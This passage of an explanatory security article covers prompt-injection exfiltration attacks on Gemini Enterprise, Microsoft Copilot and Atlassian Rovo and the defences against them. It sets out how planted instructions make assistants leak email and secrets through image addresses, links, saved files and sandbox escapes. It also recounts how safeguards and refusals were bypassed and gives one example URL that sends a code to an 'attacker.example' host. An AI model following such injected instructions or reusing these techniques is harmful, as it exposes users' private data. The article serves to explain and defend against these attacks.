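Of the five attacks, GeminiJack was the most like EchoLeak. It affected Gemini Enterprise (Google's AI tools for companies) and Vertex AI Search (a platform customers use to build their own search systems). Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data* reports that Noma found the flaw in June 2025 and told Google the same day.

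The attacker could plant instructions in a shared Google Doc, an email or a calendar invitation, and the employee did not have to open any of them. In an example from Security Affairs' *GeminiJack zero-click flaw in Gemini Enterprise allowed corporate data exfiltration*, the employee asks Gemini to "show me our budgets". Gemini retrieves the attacker's document along with the genuine ones and puts company data into the address of an image in its answer. SC Media's *Google addresses ‘GeminiJack’ exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise* lists emails, calendars and documents among the data at risk.

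As with EchoLeak, the planted document had to match something an employee would ask about. Budgets are a good choice because someone in almost every company asks about them. SecurityWeek's *Google Patches Gemini Enterprise Vulnerability Exposing Corporate Data* states that the attack "did not require any user interaction", which leaves out the employee's search.

The image leak is surprising because Google had dealt with image leaks in Bard in 2023, and Tenable found that the Gemini assistant filtered outside images. Noma's research lead, Sasi Levi, blamed unfiltered HTML output, according to TechNadu. Google's protection in one Gemini product evidently did not extend to the other, much as some of OpenAI's apps had lacked url_safe.

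Google fixed both products before Noma published its findings in December. The OECD's *Google GeminiJack AI Vulnerability Exposes Corporate Data* (2025) classifies the flaw as a hazard rather than an incident because nobody had reported actual harm.

### A login button in a Copilot diagram

Microsoft 365 Copilot can draw diagrams with Mermaid, a tool that turns text into flowcharts and similar pictures. Mermaid diagrams can contain links and have custom colours and shapes. Logue used both features to make a diagram that looked like a login button.

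His attack started with an Excel file. As Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability* describes, he hid the instructions in white text on several sheets, and they took effect when the user asked Copilot to summarise the file. Copilot then did the following:

1. It ignored the figures in the spreadsheet and told the user to log in to see the contents.
2. It used its email search tool to fetch the user's recent messages.
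3. It converted the messages to hexadecimal, which writes each character as a short code of digits and letters, and split the result into short lines because Mermaid limits their length.
4. It drew the button, with a padlock symbol on it, and put the converted messages into the button's link.

If the user clicked, the browser sent the messages to Logue's server. According to CyberMaterial, the user then saw a mock login screen, which made the button look more genuine.

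This one-click attack required the victim to ask for a summary of the attacker's file, then click after Copilot had collected the emails. Cyber Security News places the click first, writing that the attack needed no direct interaction "beyond an initial click". Red Hot Cyber reports that Logue compared his attack with an earlier one on Cursor, a programming tool, in which a Mermaid diagram loaded an outside image and leaked data without a click.

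The mailbox search and the false login request had already appeared in the 2024 attacks on Copilot and Slack AI. The diagram was new. Logue used it to get past Microsoft's filter on outside links, as Aim had done with unusual link notation. Such a filter has to cover more formats as Microsoft adds features.

Logue reported the attack on 15 August 2025, after discussions at the DEF CON security conference, according to Rewterz's *Microsoft 365 Copilot prompt injection flaw enables data theft*. Microsoft fixed the flaw by making the diagrams static, so users can no longer click anything in them. daily.dev's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Arbitrary Data Exfiltration via Mermaid Diagrams* adds that he received no reward because Microsoft's bounty programme did not cover the product. Microsoft now pays for reports of flaws in Microsoft 365 Copilot that it rates critical or important.

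### The five attacks compared

| Attack and product | Who can plant the text | What the victim does | What the attacker can take | How the data leaves | What the vendor changed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| ShadowLeak, ChatGPT Deep Research | Anyone who can email the victim | Asks for research on their own mail | Personal data from the inbox | OpenAI's servers open the attacker's web address | OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from altering addresses, then restricted links from emails after a bypass |
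| ForcedLeak, Salesforce Agentforce | Anyone who can fill in the company's web form | Asks the agent about the new lead | Customer records, such as leads' email addresses | The browser loads an image from an expired domain still on the allowlist | Salesforce took back the domain and limited agents to trusted addresses |
| CamoLeak, GitHub Copilot Chat | Anyone who can open a pull request | Asks Copilot to explain the pull request | Keys, code and reports from private projects | The browser loads one image per character through GitHub's proxy | GitHub turned off images in Copilot Chat |
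| GeminiJack, Gemini Enterprise and Vertex AI Search | Anyone who can share a document or send an email or calendar invitation | Runs an ordinary search on a matching subject | Emails, calendar entries and documents | The browser loads an image with the data in its address | Google repaired both products |
| Mermaid attack, Microsoft 365 Copilot | Anyone who can get an Excel file to the victim | Asks for a summary of the file, then clicks the false login button | Recent emails | The browser opens the link in the diagram | Microsoft removed clickable content from diagrams |

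## 2026: new leaks from Microsoft Copilot and Atlassian Rovo

During 2026 the security company Varonis published three attacks on Microsoft's AI assistants, each of which started with the victim clicking a link. Other researchers extracted data from Microsoft 365 Copilot and Atlassian's assistant Rovo by planting instructions in a document. In December the team that had found EchoLeak published ReLeak, three attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot that needed only an unread email.

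Microsoft has two easily confused products named Copilot, and a flaw in one may not exist in the other. Microsoft 365 Copilot is the enterprise assistant and can access a worker's company mail, files and chats. Copilot Personal is a consumer assistant that can read services such as Gmail if the user connects them.

### Reprompt: a prompt inside a link

Many chat pages accept a question in their web address. An address ending in `?q=harbour+contract` opens the page with those words already in the input box. Varonis exploited this feature in Reprompt, an attack on Copilot Personal that it published in January 2026. The attacker replaces the question with instructions and sends the victim the link. According to eSecurity Planet's *Microsoft Copilot Reprompt Attack Enables Stealthy Data Exfiltration*, Copilot ran the instructions as soon as the page loaded, so clicking the link had the same effect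 as typing them and pressing Enter.

The text in a Reprompt link reached the model as the user's own question, unlike instructions in an email, which arrive as outside content that the software can label or filter. Even a model that perfectly separated the user's words from everyone else's would therefore have followed the text in the link.

Copilot refused some questionable web requests and removed some sensitive data from its answers, but these safeguards seemed strongest on the first attempt, so Varonis told Copilot to do everything twice. The attacker's server then sent further instructions based on Copilot's earlier answers, so the attacker did not have to decide in advance what to look for. SecurityWeek reported that the leak could continue after the victim closed the chat. According to BeyondMachines, Varonis told Microsoft about the flaw on 31 August 2025, and Microsoft patched it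 on 13 January 2026.

### SearchLeak: the same trick in the enterprise product

In June 2026 Varonis showed that a link could also carry a prompt into Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise Search, which searches a company's emails, meetings and files. Taler (2026), in *SearchLeak*, writes that the researchers were surprised that a technique from the consumer product worked there, because enterprise products are supposed to have additional guardrails.

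The link led to a genuine Microsoft site, so phishing filters were unlikely to block it. When the victim clicked it, Copilot searched their mailbox and put a message's title into the address of an image. Microsoft had two defences that should have stopped the image from loading.

One of them turned any HTML in Copilot's answer into plain text, so that the browser would display the code instead of acting on it. But this happened only once the answer was complete. Copilot displays an answer piece by piece as the model generates it, so the browser requested the image in the code before Copilot converted the code to text.

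The other defence was the page's content security policy, which blocked images from unknown servers but allowed them from bing.com. Bing has a search-by-image function. A user supplies the address of a picture, and Bing's servers fetch the picture to analyse it. With the Bing part replaced, the image address looked roughly like this:

`https://image-search.example/find?picture=attacker.example/Your_code_is_482193`

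The browser contacted Bing, Bing's server contacted the attacker's server, and the email's title appeared in the attacker's log. A year earlier, Aim had got past Microsoft's policy in much the same way, with a server-side fetch in Teams. Taler advises security teams to treat any allowed domain that fetches user-supplied addresses as a potential exfiltration channel.

Even an email's subject line can be sensitive, because many services put one-time login codes there. Taler also lists the text of emails, meeting notes and salary files among the data at risk. This is a reasonable inference from what Copilot can search, but the published example extracts only a subject line.

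Microsoft assigned the flaw CVE-2026-42824 on 4 June, according to The Next Web. The Hacker News, in *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw* (2026), noted that Microsoft rated the flaw critical but gave it a CVSS score of only 6.5. ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* reports that Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers and described it as command injection, as it had first described EchoLeak. Nobody had reported a real attack.

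### CoSnitch: Copilot Personal again

Varonis published its third attack, CoSnitch, which affected Copilot Personal, on 18 August. Normally, a prompt in a link only filled in the input box, and the user had to press Enter to run it. If the link also contained a second, undocumented parameter, the prompt ran automatically.

Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes how the researchers learned about this parameter by questioning Copilot. They asked why a prompt could not run without the user's involvement and followed each refusal with another question. Copilot's explanations became more technical, until one included the parameter's name and a list of the protections that had supposedly disabled it. Language models often invent such details, so the answer was of little use until the researchers tested the parameter and found that it still worked. Radware had obtained a similar hint in 2025 by asking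 ChatGPT's Deep Research what tools it had.

Once the prompt was running, Copilot searched the victim's connected Gmail account, put what it found into a web address, and opened that address as though to summarise the page. In one test, Copilot retrieved the body of an email containing a password. Copilot's page-fetching feature made the outgoing request, so the browser's content security policy did not apply. The prompt ran to the end even if the victim closed the tab immediately.

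In a separate demonstration, the victim asked Copilot to summarise a web page, and hidden text on the page added an instruction to Copilot's memory. Rehberger had done the same to ChatGPT in 2024. The user can delete the planted memory in the settings, although Varonis calls it permanent. Until they do, it can affect every conversation, for example by making Copilot tell the user that a known vulnerability is harmless.

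The CoSnitch flaw was in the consumer product, Copilot Personal, as the United Nations University (UNU) points out, though Varonis writes that CoSnitch takes data from enterprises. It exposed a company's data only if an employee had brought it into Copilot Personal, for instance by connecting an account used for work. Varonis reported the flaw in December 2025, and Microsoft shipped its patches about eight months later, on the day of publication. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* gives the flaw's identifier as CVE-2026-24301.

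Rehberger found flaws in the consumer and enterprise versions of Microsoft Copilot. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes an HTML preview that could send data out and a Copilot version of his ChatGPT memory attack. He reported the flaws in 2025, and Microsoft has since patched them (CVE-2026-24299).

### Atlassian Rovo: a link and an uploaded file

Atlassian makes Jira, which teams use to track tasks, and Confluence, where they write shared documents. Its assistant, Rovo, searches both and can connect to more than 50 other platforms, including Slack and Microsoft 365. Two security companies published attacks on Rovo in the first week of August 2026.

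In *RovoBlast*, Varonis again used a link. It carried instructions in a parameter that Rovo accepts for starting a chat, and one click ran them with the victim's access rights. In the demonstration, Rovo found a private API key in Confluence and sent it out in the address of an image. Varonis also tested the technique on Jira and on data from connected SharePoint and Outlook accounts. Atlassian fixed the flaw on 8 July and paid a $6,000 reward, according to The Hacker News (2026). Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant* reports that Varonis presented the attack at DEF CON before publishing it on 7 August.

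Two days earlier, PromptArmor had published *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls*, which describes a user who uploads a guide to organising a backlog of tasks, perhaps one found online, and asks Rovo to organise their Jira tickets. Rovo searches Jira and Confluence as requested, but hidden instructions in the guide make it add what it finds to a URL on the attacker's server and open that URL without asking for approval. A user who returns to the chat later sees suggested ticket updates and no trace of the leak.

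Administrators can turn off web search in Rovo for the whole organisation, but this did not stop such a request. Rovo kept the tool for opening search results, which also opened addresses that Rovo had just generated. OpenAI's crawler rule blocks this kind of address in ChatGPT. PromptArmor also reported that Rovo displayed Markdown images, which might have provided another way to leak data, but did not demonstrate an attack through them.

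PromptArmor calls the attack zero-click. The Hacker News disagrees, because the victim has to give Rovo the attacker's file and then ask for something. PromptArmor demonstrated the attack with an uploaded file, but says the instructions could also come from other content that Rovo reads, such as a support ticket from outside the company. An attack that began with a ticket could be zero-click in the same sense as EchoLeak.

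PromptArmor had reported the problem on 23 May. Atlassian assigned a case number two days later. PromptArmor wrote again on 4 June and 29 July, received no further reply, and published on 5 August while Rovo was still vulnerable. The Hacker News could confirm a fix only for the link attack. Neither company had said whether the July repair also affected uploaded files.

PromptArmor's demonstration contradicts an article on Atlassian Community, the company's user forum, which said that hidden instructions in a file could not trick Rovo. The article, which is not an official security advisory, said that Rovo filters uploaded files and treats their contents as data instead of commands. Rovo can index a file as data, but the text still enters the model's context, where the model may follow it.

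### ChatMate and the code interpreter

Language models are unreliable at arithmetic, so Microsoft 365 Copilot has a code interpreter. When a user asks for a chart or a calculation, the model writes a short Python program, Copilot runs it, and the model reads the result. The program runs in a sandbox, an isolated environment that should keep it away from the network and the rest of Microsoft's systems.

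On 6 August 2026, Rubrik Zero Labs, the research team of a data security company, published an attack that broke this isolation. *Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate* (Lahav, 2026) describes how the attack begins when a user asks Copilot about a document containing hidden instructions. The instructions make Copilot run code that escapes the sandbox and connects to the attacker. The attacker can then type prompts into the victim's Copilot session, read the complete answers and ask follow-up questions.

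ChatMate let an attacker search the victim's data one question at a time, whereas in EchoLeak, Aim had to put all its instructions in an email and could get only what was in the context when Copilot read it. Lahav calls ChatMate's technique "remote prompt execution" and describes ChatMate as the first documented case. He acknowledges that Reprompt was closely related, since its server also adapted its instructions to Copilot's answers, but Varonis had not publicly shown a person freely controlling the session.

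The flaw is CVE-2026-32193, with a CVSS score of 8.8. In *Copilot Cowork Sandbox Bypass Gives Attackers Remote Control*, PromptArmor reports another sandbox failure in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork agent, which let a malicious Skill (an add-on) receive commands from outside and send back mail and files.

### ReLeak: three attacks from an unread email

On 3 December 2026, Simonovich published the three ReLeak attacks for Cato AI Labs, formerly Aim Labs. Cato Networks bought Aim Security in September 2025 (Faisal, 2026, *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*).

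All three attacks start the way EchoLeak did, with an email that the victim doesn't have to read. They take effect when the victim asks Microsoft 365 Copilot an ordinary work question that causes it to retrieve the email.

Microsoft's XPIA classifier, which is supposed to catch such emails, blocked none of the three attacks. Colantuoni (2026) reports in *ReLeak: furto di dati tramite Microsoft 365 Copilot* that Copilot would not carry out direct commands but could be made to follow instructions that looked like legitimate requests. Aim had likewise worded its 2025 email as a request to the recipient. Microsoft had known about this technique for well over a year when Cato reported the new attacks.

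Cato's researchers built ReLeak to test Copilot and reported it to Microsoft, and they knew of no affected customers. In its headline, *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (Fadilpašić, 2026) calls ReLeak a "campaign" to steal data from victims, but in security reporting that word usually means a series of attacks on real targets.

### Chain one: an image that Bing fetches

The first attack exploits CVE-2026-124115. Like the leak from Dana's firm, it uses a Markdown image, but the image address leads to Bing, which the browser is allowed to contact. Bing then passes the request, including the private data in the address, to the attacker's server.

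SearchLeak had also sent data out through Bing, six months before Cato's publication. Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, calls the two channels similar and notes that SearchLeak required a click. SearchLeak used the address of Bing's search-by-image function. Antipov does not say whether ReLeak used the same address, so there is not enough evidence to conclude that Cato reused it.

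If the address was the same, Microsoft's June repair had stopped SearchLeak at an earlier step, perhaps by no longer running prompts from links, and had left the route through Bing open. If the address was different, Bing had at least two functions that would forward data to an outside server. Either way, Copilot's page still trusted Bing after Varonis had shown that an attacker could use it as a relay.

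### Chain two: a file that nobody opens

Copilot can create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files and save them in OneDrive or SharePoint, Microsoft's file storage and sharing services. In the second attack, the planted instructions make Copilot save one of these files with a link whose address contains confidential data. Microsoft's servers then follow the link. This flaw is CVE-2026-124132.

In Cato's tests, the request reached the researchers' server one to eight minutes after the chat ended. Pixel Magazine's *Três ataques zero-click ao Microsoft 365 Copilot já foram corrigidos* (2026) says the user did not have to open the file and attributes the request to Microsoft's background processing. File services often scan new documents to create previews or check for malicious links, and a similar process may have sent this request.

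Slack's link previews caused the same problem in 2024, when Slack's servers fetched any address that a chatbot posted. In both cases the vendor's software opened a link as a convenience or a precaution, without detecting that a model had put private data into it.

The delay would make the leak hard to notice. Dana might have closed Copilot before the price left Microsoft's servers, and her company's network would have no record of the request. However, a saved file should remain in storage until someone deletes it, unlike an image in a chat answer, which can disappear with the chat. An investigator who knew what to look for could search for recently created files with strange links.

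### Chain three: code that reaches the network

The third attack used the code interpreter. Microsoft promised in its documentation that no network traffic could enter or leave the sandbox. Cato's researchers broke that isolation and had Copilot run a program that sent confidential data directly to their server. The attack did not need a link or an image, and no other Microsoft service had to forward the data.

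An image address has limited room, but a program can, in principle, compress a long document, split it into pieces and send them one after another. This makes the network block especially important, because without it the interpreter is a general-purpose tool for sending data out.

Microsoft rated the flaw, CVE-2026-78501, critical, with a CVSS score of 8.6, up from an initial 7.4. ChatMate has a different CVE, so Microsoft evidently treated the two as separate flaws, but both involved code escaping the same kind of isolation. Rubrik published ChatMate on 6 August, in the middle of the three weeks when Cato was sending its reports to Microsoft.

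Companies can also add the code interpreter to agents they build with Microsoft's Agent Builder and Copilot Studio. Antipov notes that nobody has confirmed whether the flaws affected those agents.

### How the attacks got around the EchoLeak defences

In 2025 Aim had to get past a filter that removed outside links and images from Copilot's answers, and then past the content security policy. The ReLeak attacks met these defences in different ways:

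| Attack | Filter on links and images in the answer | Content security policy | What sent the data to the attacker |
|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak (2025) | Missed an unusual Markdown notation | Allowed a Teams domain | A Teams server |
| ReLeak, chain one | Did not stop the image | Allowed Bing | A Bing server |
| ReLeak, chain two | Did not prevent the leak, because the link was in a saved file | Did not apply, because no browser made the request | Microsoft's file processing |
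| ReLeak, chain three | Had nothing to remove, because the data did not leave through the answer | Did not apply, because no browser made the request | The program in the code interpreter |

Chain one nearly repeats EchoLeak, using Bing instead of Teams. A stricter image filter or a shorter list of allowed domains could have stopped it.

Neither change would have helped against the other two chains. Microsoft built those defences around the chat window, where the earlier leaks happened, but Copilot can now also write files and run programs. To stop chain two, Microsoft had to control what Copilot puts in a file or what its servers do with the file afterwards. To stop chain three, it had to make the sandbox as isolated as documented.

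Faisal writes that each ability Copilot gained, including its handling of images, became a new way for data to leave. This is true of files and code, but EchoLeak had already used images to extract data, and Rehberger had reported the same route in Bing Chat in 2023.

### AI agents as testers

Cato found the flaws with the help of other AI agents. Under the researchers' supervision, the agents wrote test scenarios, analysed Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempt. Radware's researchers had done this by hand in 2025, rewording their email to Deep Research until it succeeded.

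Automated systems are well suited to this kind of work. Trying an instruction that fails takes little effort, and the refusal may contain a hint about what to change. A filter that blocks 99 out of 100 attempts protects well against someone who sends one email, but much less well against someone who can test thousands of versions on their own Copilot account and send only the one that works. Attackers can use this method as well as researchers, as Pixel Magazine implies when it describes AI tools testing companies' AI for weaknesses.

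It is less clear how much time the agents saved. The team had already learned how Copilot worked during its EchoLeak research, so even if ReLeak took less time, the agents would not be the only reason.

### Microsoft's repairs and the finders' verdict

Cato reported the three attacks between 29 July and 20 August 2026. Microsoft fixed the code interpreter flaw on 17 September, the saved-files flaw on 11 November and the Bing image flaw on 15 November. The image attack was the most familiar of the three, but it took the longest to fix, at least 12 weeks from Cato's report.

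Microsoft made the changes on its own servers, and its advisory says that customers need to take no action. Pixel Magazine tells readers that the problem is solved for anyone who keeps Microsoft 365 up to date, but customers had nothing to update.

After EchoLeak, Microsoft promised further layers of defence in a statement to Fortune (2025). Cato concluded that "too little progress has been made" since then. Its researchers think the underlying weakness is still that Copilot cannot reliably tell untrusted content from legitimate instructions.

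The evidence supports this verdict for the first half of the attack. An email from a stranger could still enter the context and direct the model, and the classifier failed against all three versions. Cato sells AI security products, so it has a commercial reason to emphasise the failure. Its successful attacks also do not show how many other emails Copilot resisted, so we cannot tell from them whether the classifier had become harder to fool.

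Progress on the second half is harder to judge. None of the ReLeak attacks used EchoLeak's Teams address, which suggests that Microsoft had closed that route. But the team reported three other routes within about three weeks, so closing them one at a time had still left attackers with alternatives.

Microsoft's changes in autumn 2026 may also have been broader than the three fixes. When Cato published, two of the three CVE entries were still marked "reserved", meaning their full records had not yet appeared.

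## Blocking the exfiltration channels, and why gaps remain

In nearly all of these leaks, private data left in a request to a server that the attacker could read. A control that stops one kind of request may not stop another, so it helps to sort the exfiltration channels by who or what makes the request.

| Who or what makes the request | Example | Control meant to stop it |
|---|---|---|
| The user, by clicking a link | Mermaid | Removing outside links from answers, or warning the user before one opens |
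| The browser, by loading an image | ForcedLeak | A content security policy, or no outside images |
| The vendor's server, by fetching a page or previewing a link | ShadowLeak | Limits on the addresses the server may open, or no previews |
| A later process, by opening a saved file | ReLeak | Removing outside links from generated files, or not following them |
| Code that the assistant runs | ChatMate | Network isolation |

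Some attacks combine two channels. In EchoLeak, the browser loaded an image from a Microsoft server, and that server made the request that reached Aim.

The channel can also depend on the program that displays the answer. PromptArmor points out that a link in a chat window does nothing until someone clicks it, but a messaging app with previews requests the same link automatically. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API logs unpatched data exfiltration* describes an app that blocked an answer containing a malicious image, but the image loaded when someone later opened that conversation in OpenAI's log viewer. A vendor therefore has to protect every place where an answer might appear.

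### Why link filters miss links

A link filter fails when the program that displays the answer recognises a link or image notation that the filter does not, as happened in EchoLeak. Besides the notations Aim tried, Markdown accepts an address by itself in angle brackets, and some chat windows also accept HTML. Developers can add each notation to the filter once someone reports it, but unreported ones can still get through.

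Filtering after the conversion is safer, because by then the different spellings have all become the same few kinds of page element. The filter also has to finish before the browser acts on the result. In SearchLeak, the filter finished too late, a fault that TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool* calls a race condition.

Other filters, such as data loss prevention software, look for the private data itself and can block, for example, a request containing something that resembles an API key. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) built an agent on a small open model and had it summarise web pages containing planted instructions to send out private data. The agent sent the data in about 89% of 480 runs. Checks on the final answer missed 95% of the successful attacks because the summary looked harmless. When the attack split the secret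 over several requests, measured leakage per request fell by 73%, and the pieces got past simple data loss checks.

The 89% figure comes from a weak model with minimal standing instructions, so it should not be applied to Copilot or ChatGPT. The result about splitting depends less on the model, because any check that examines one request at a time can miss a key split across several requests.

### Why allowed domains leak

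In the same tests, controls on the network, such as limiting the agent to approved domains, worked considerably better than defences in the prompt. But an allowlist only controls where the first request goes, and the past cases show three ways in which an approved domain can pass data to an attacker:

- It may fetch any address it receives, as services at Bing and Teams did.
- It may host anyone's code or storage, like Google's Apps Script and Microsoft's windows.net.
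- Its registration may lapse, which let Noma buy a domain that Salesforce still allowed.

Redirects are another weakness, but software can follow them and check every address along the way, which Lan and colleagues found effective. This method would not have stopped EchoLeak, because the Teams server made the second request itself.

Shorter allowlists and narrower entries both help. A content security policy can allow one folder on a domain instead of the whole domain, so a page that needs Bing's thumbnails would not have to allow Bing's search-by-image function as well. Someone still has to check what each allowed address can be used for, and check again when the service behind it changes.

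Companies can also monitor their network traffic for leaks, as trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* recommends. This works best when the browser contacts the attacker directly. If the request goes through an approved domain, the private data is in the rest of the URL, which encryption hides from the company unless it decrypts its employees' traffic.

### How much data fits through a channel

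If the model can write any address, one request can carry hundreds of characters of data. For example, an address might have room for 500 characters, each a letter from a to z or a digit. Each character has 36 possible values, so it carries log₂ 36, or about 5.17, bits (a bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question), and the whole request carries about 2,585 bits.

Some controls prevent the model from writing new addresses but still let it choose among addresses the attacker prepared. With *N* fixed addresses, each request carries log₂ *N* bits. A random 20-character secret made of the same 36 symbols holds 20 × 5.17, or about 103 bits, so the number of requests needed is 103 divided by log₂ *N*, rounded up. The last column shows the requests needed for a seven-digit number, such as the price in Dana's bid.

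| Fixed addresses | Bits per request | Requests for a 20-character secret | Requests for a seven-digit number |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1.00 | 104 | 24 |
| 9 | 3.17 | 33 | 8 |
| 36 | 5.17 | 20 | 5 |
| 1,000 | 9.97 | 11 | 3 |

The row for nine addresses corresponds to the 2023 test of url_safe on Embrace The Red. An attacker can encode any text by using the nine addresses as digits in base nine, so the secret doesn't have to be spelled with the nine letters that pass. Reaching the minimum of 33 requests requires converting the whole secret into one large number, which a language model would probably get wrong without running code. It is easier to send each character as two requests, which works because nine addresses make 81 pairs, but this takes 40 requests.

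These figures hold only if every request arrives, the attacker can work out the order in which the model made the choices, and loading the same address twice produces two requests. The last two conditions often fail in browsers. According to Embrace The Red, browsers cache images, and requests can arrive out of order. If the attacker learns only which of the 36 addresses the browser loaded, and not their order or any repeats, the channel carries at most 36 bits in total, far too few for the 20-character secret.

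Attackers can get around this by preparing more addresses. Radware made a separate set for each position in a block of text, so "a" in first place had a different address from "a" in second place. This takes 36 addresses per position, or 720 for a 20-character secret. The model uses each address at most once, so the order of requests and stored copies of pages don't matter. For the same reason, Rehberger's proposed ban on visiting the same address twice in a session would not stop the attack.

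A limit on the number of requests is more effective, at least against large leaks. If ChatGPT loaded only one image per answer, an attacker with 36 addresses would need 20 answers to obtain the secret and five to obtain Dana's price, and copying a long email would be impractical. But a single request can reveal whether Dana's firm intends to bid, so only a limit of zero would prevent that leak.

### Removing images and asking the user

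The surest way to close the browser's image channel is to load no outside images, as GitHub chose for Copilot Chat. Because the browser then sends no image requests to outside servers, an attacker can't leak data through them, even with a relay on an allowed domain or a set of prepared addresses that each stand for a character. Users lose photographs and charts from the web. A vendor could keep these by fetching each image on its own server and passing it to the browser, but the attacker's server would still receive a request, as it did in CamoLeak. Removing outside images leaves the other four channels open.

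For links, a vendor can ask the user first. When ChatGPT is about to send a third party something it learned in the conversation, OpenAI's Safe Url check is supposed to either block the request or show the user the information and ask for confirmation. Similarly, Canvas (ChatGPT's workspace for documents and code) and ChatGPT apps run in a sandbox meant to detect unexpected communication and ask for consent.

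Requiring approval lets the user refuse a leak that would otherwise be silent, but only if they recognise that something is wrong. A person may notice a salary figure in an address but is unlikely to notice the same figure in Base64, and an address that stands for a single letter contains nothing suspicious. OpenAI warns that frequent false alarms can train people to click through, which was one of its reasons for rejecting a strict list of trusted sites. Approval also makes the assistant less useful for unattended work, because a task may stop halfway to wait for an answer.

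### Opening only addresses that are already public

Under OpenAI's January 2026 rule, ChatGPT automatically loads only addresses that the company's crawler has already recorded. This blocks the 2,585-bit request in the example above, but an attacker can still send data through the choice of which indexed page to load. With 36 pages to choose from, each request carries about 5 bits, roughly one five-hundredth of the earlier capacity.

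The attacker can recover some capacity by publishing more pages and waiting for the crawler to find them. A thousand pages would double the capacity to about 10 bits, but doubling it again to about 20 would take a million. The planted text also has to tell the model what each page stands for. The rule works well against bulk theft but much less well against theft of short secrets such as passwords and login codes.

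Addresses in the user's own message may be another gap. Rehberger believes, according to Embrace The Red, that ChatGPT also treats these as safe for the rest of the session. This is convenient because people often paste a link and ask about it. But Schwartzman's 2024 attack relied on a victim pasting a long piece of code that contained the attacker's addresses. If ChatGPT doesn't distinguish addresses the user typed from those buried in pasted text, an attacker could use the same trick to supply prepared addresses without waiting for a crawler.

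The rule is a modest inconvenience to users because the index may not include a newly published page or a document reachable only through an unlisted link. It also covers only leaks through the web address, so an assistant that can post a comment or send an email can still leak data that way.

In an encouraging outside test, *The Framing Gap* (2026) compared ChatGPT with an OpenAI model accessed directly through the API. The bare model leaked a secret in up to 100% of trials, depending on the wording of the attack, while ChatGPT leaked nothing in 48 valid trials. The researchers could not see inside ChatGPT, so they did not attribute the difference to the link rule or any other cause. With only 48 trials, the result is also consistent with a true leak rate of up to about 6%, at the 95% confidence level.

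### Lockdown Mode

Lockdown Mode closes the gap that the public-address rule leaves in browsing. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) explains that browsing in this mode uses only cached pages, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network. However many pages an attacker has in the cache, their server receives no request that would reveal which ones ChatGPT reads.

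The mode substantially limits what ChatGPT can do. According to OpenAI's help page, it disables Deep Research and Agent Mode. ChatGPT cannot download files for analysis, code written in Canvas cannot use the network, and search results may be out of date or missing. OpenAI designed the mode for a small group of users at unusual risk, such as executives and security teams, and said that most people did not need it. In June 2026, OpenAI began offering it to personal accounts too. Users can switch the mode off for a single chat, which makes it more convenient, but their protection then depends on knowing which chats are risky.

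On personal accounts, Lockdown Mode blocks live access to outside services when it conflicts with the mode's protections. In company-managed workspaces, it does not automatically disable every app, and the administrator has to decide which apps and actions to allow. OpenAI advises against allowing any action that writes data where an outsider might see it, even in a trusted app. Reading from a trusted app carries less risk of leaking data directly, but it can still supply private data for an attacker to send out through another channel. An approved app could therefore leave a channel open even with Lockdown Mode on. The mode also does not affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's programming assistant.

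The bypass that became public in November 2026 exploited a flaw outside these exceptions. Capstone Technologies Group's *ChatGPT Lockdown Mode Bypass Exfiltrates Chats Without User Interaction* places the flaw in the HTML previews of ChatGPT's desktop app and credits the security company Check Point with finding it. A popup window opened from the preview escaped the sandbox and could send chat data to an attacker's server. The restriction on browsing still worked, but the app contained another component that could make requests. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reported that attackers could reach the entire chat history. OpenAI had already fixed the flaw on 18 September.

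### Isolating code from the network

A program the assistant runs can send data in any form and any number of times, so limits on links and images do not constrain it. The remedy is to run it in a sandbox with no network connection. The assistant can still calculate, draw charts and analyse files that the user supplies, but it cannot download a missing software library, look up today's exchange rate or test a program against a live service.

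Programmers often need those functions, so Codex lets them turn internet access on. OpenAI labels the setting "Elevated Risk" and lets users restrict it with an allowlist of domains and a choice of permitted HTTP methods, the types of request a program may make. The allowlist has the weaknesses described above, and they may matter more here because sites where programmers download code often let anyone upload it too. Limiting the methods can prevent a program from submitting a form or uploading a file in the usual way, but data can still leak through the address in a GET request, the ordinary way to request a page or picture. Dana's browser sent out the price in a GET request.

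Full isolation depends on the block working, and both ChatMate and the third ReLeak attack got past Microsoft's block. An ordinary test, in which a program tries and fails to open a web page, shows only that the obvious route is closed. A vendor can depend less on the sandbox by adding a second block outside it, for instance on the machine's network connection, so that a program that escapes the sandbox still cannot reach the internet.

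Even a perfectly isolated program must return its results to the assistant, which needs them to answer the question. If the program compresses a contract into a short string and returns that string, the model can put it into a link, an image address or a saved file.

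## Keeping the assistant from obeying outside content

Dana's firm would also have kept its bid secret if the stranger's email had never reached the model, or if the model had ignored the request in it. Microsoft distinguishes probabilistic defences, which only make an attack less likely to succeed, from deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack fails whatever the model does. It prefers deterministic defences, but says that nobody yet knows how to detect every injection with certainty. Filters, markings and training are therefore probabilistic, while rules about which data may go where can be deterministic.

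### Filters for hostile instructions

To train an injection classifier, developers collect texts with and without injections, label each one, and adjust the classifier until it scores the texts with injections higher than the rest. They then choose a score above which the software blocks a text. Microsoft offers developers one such classifier, Prompt Shields, which it trained on known injection techniques in several languages and updates as new techniques appear.

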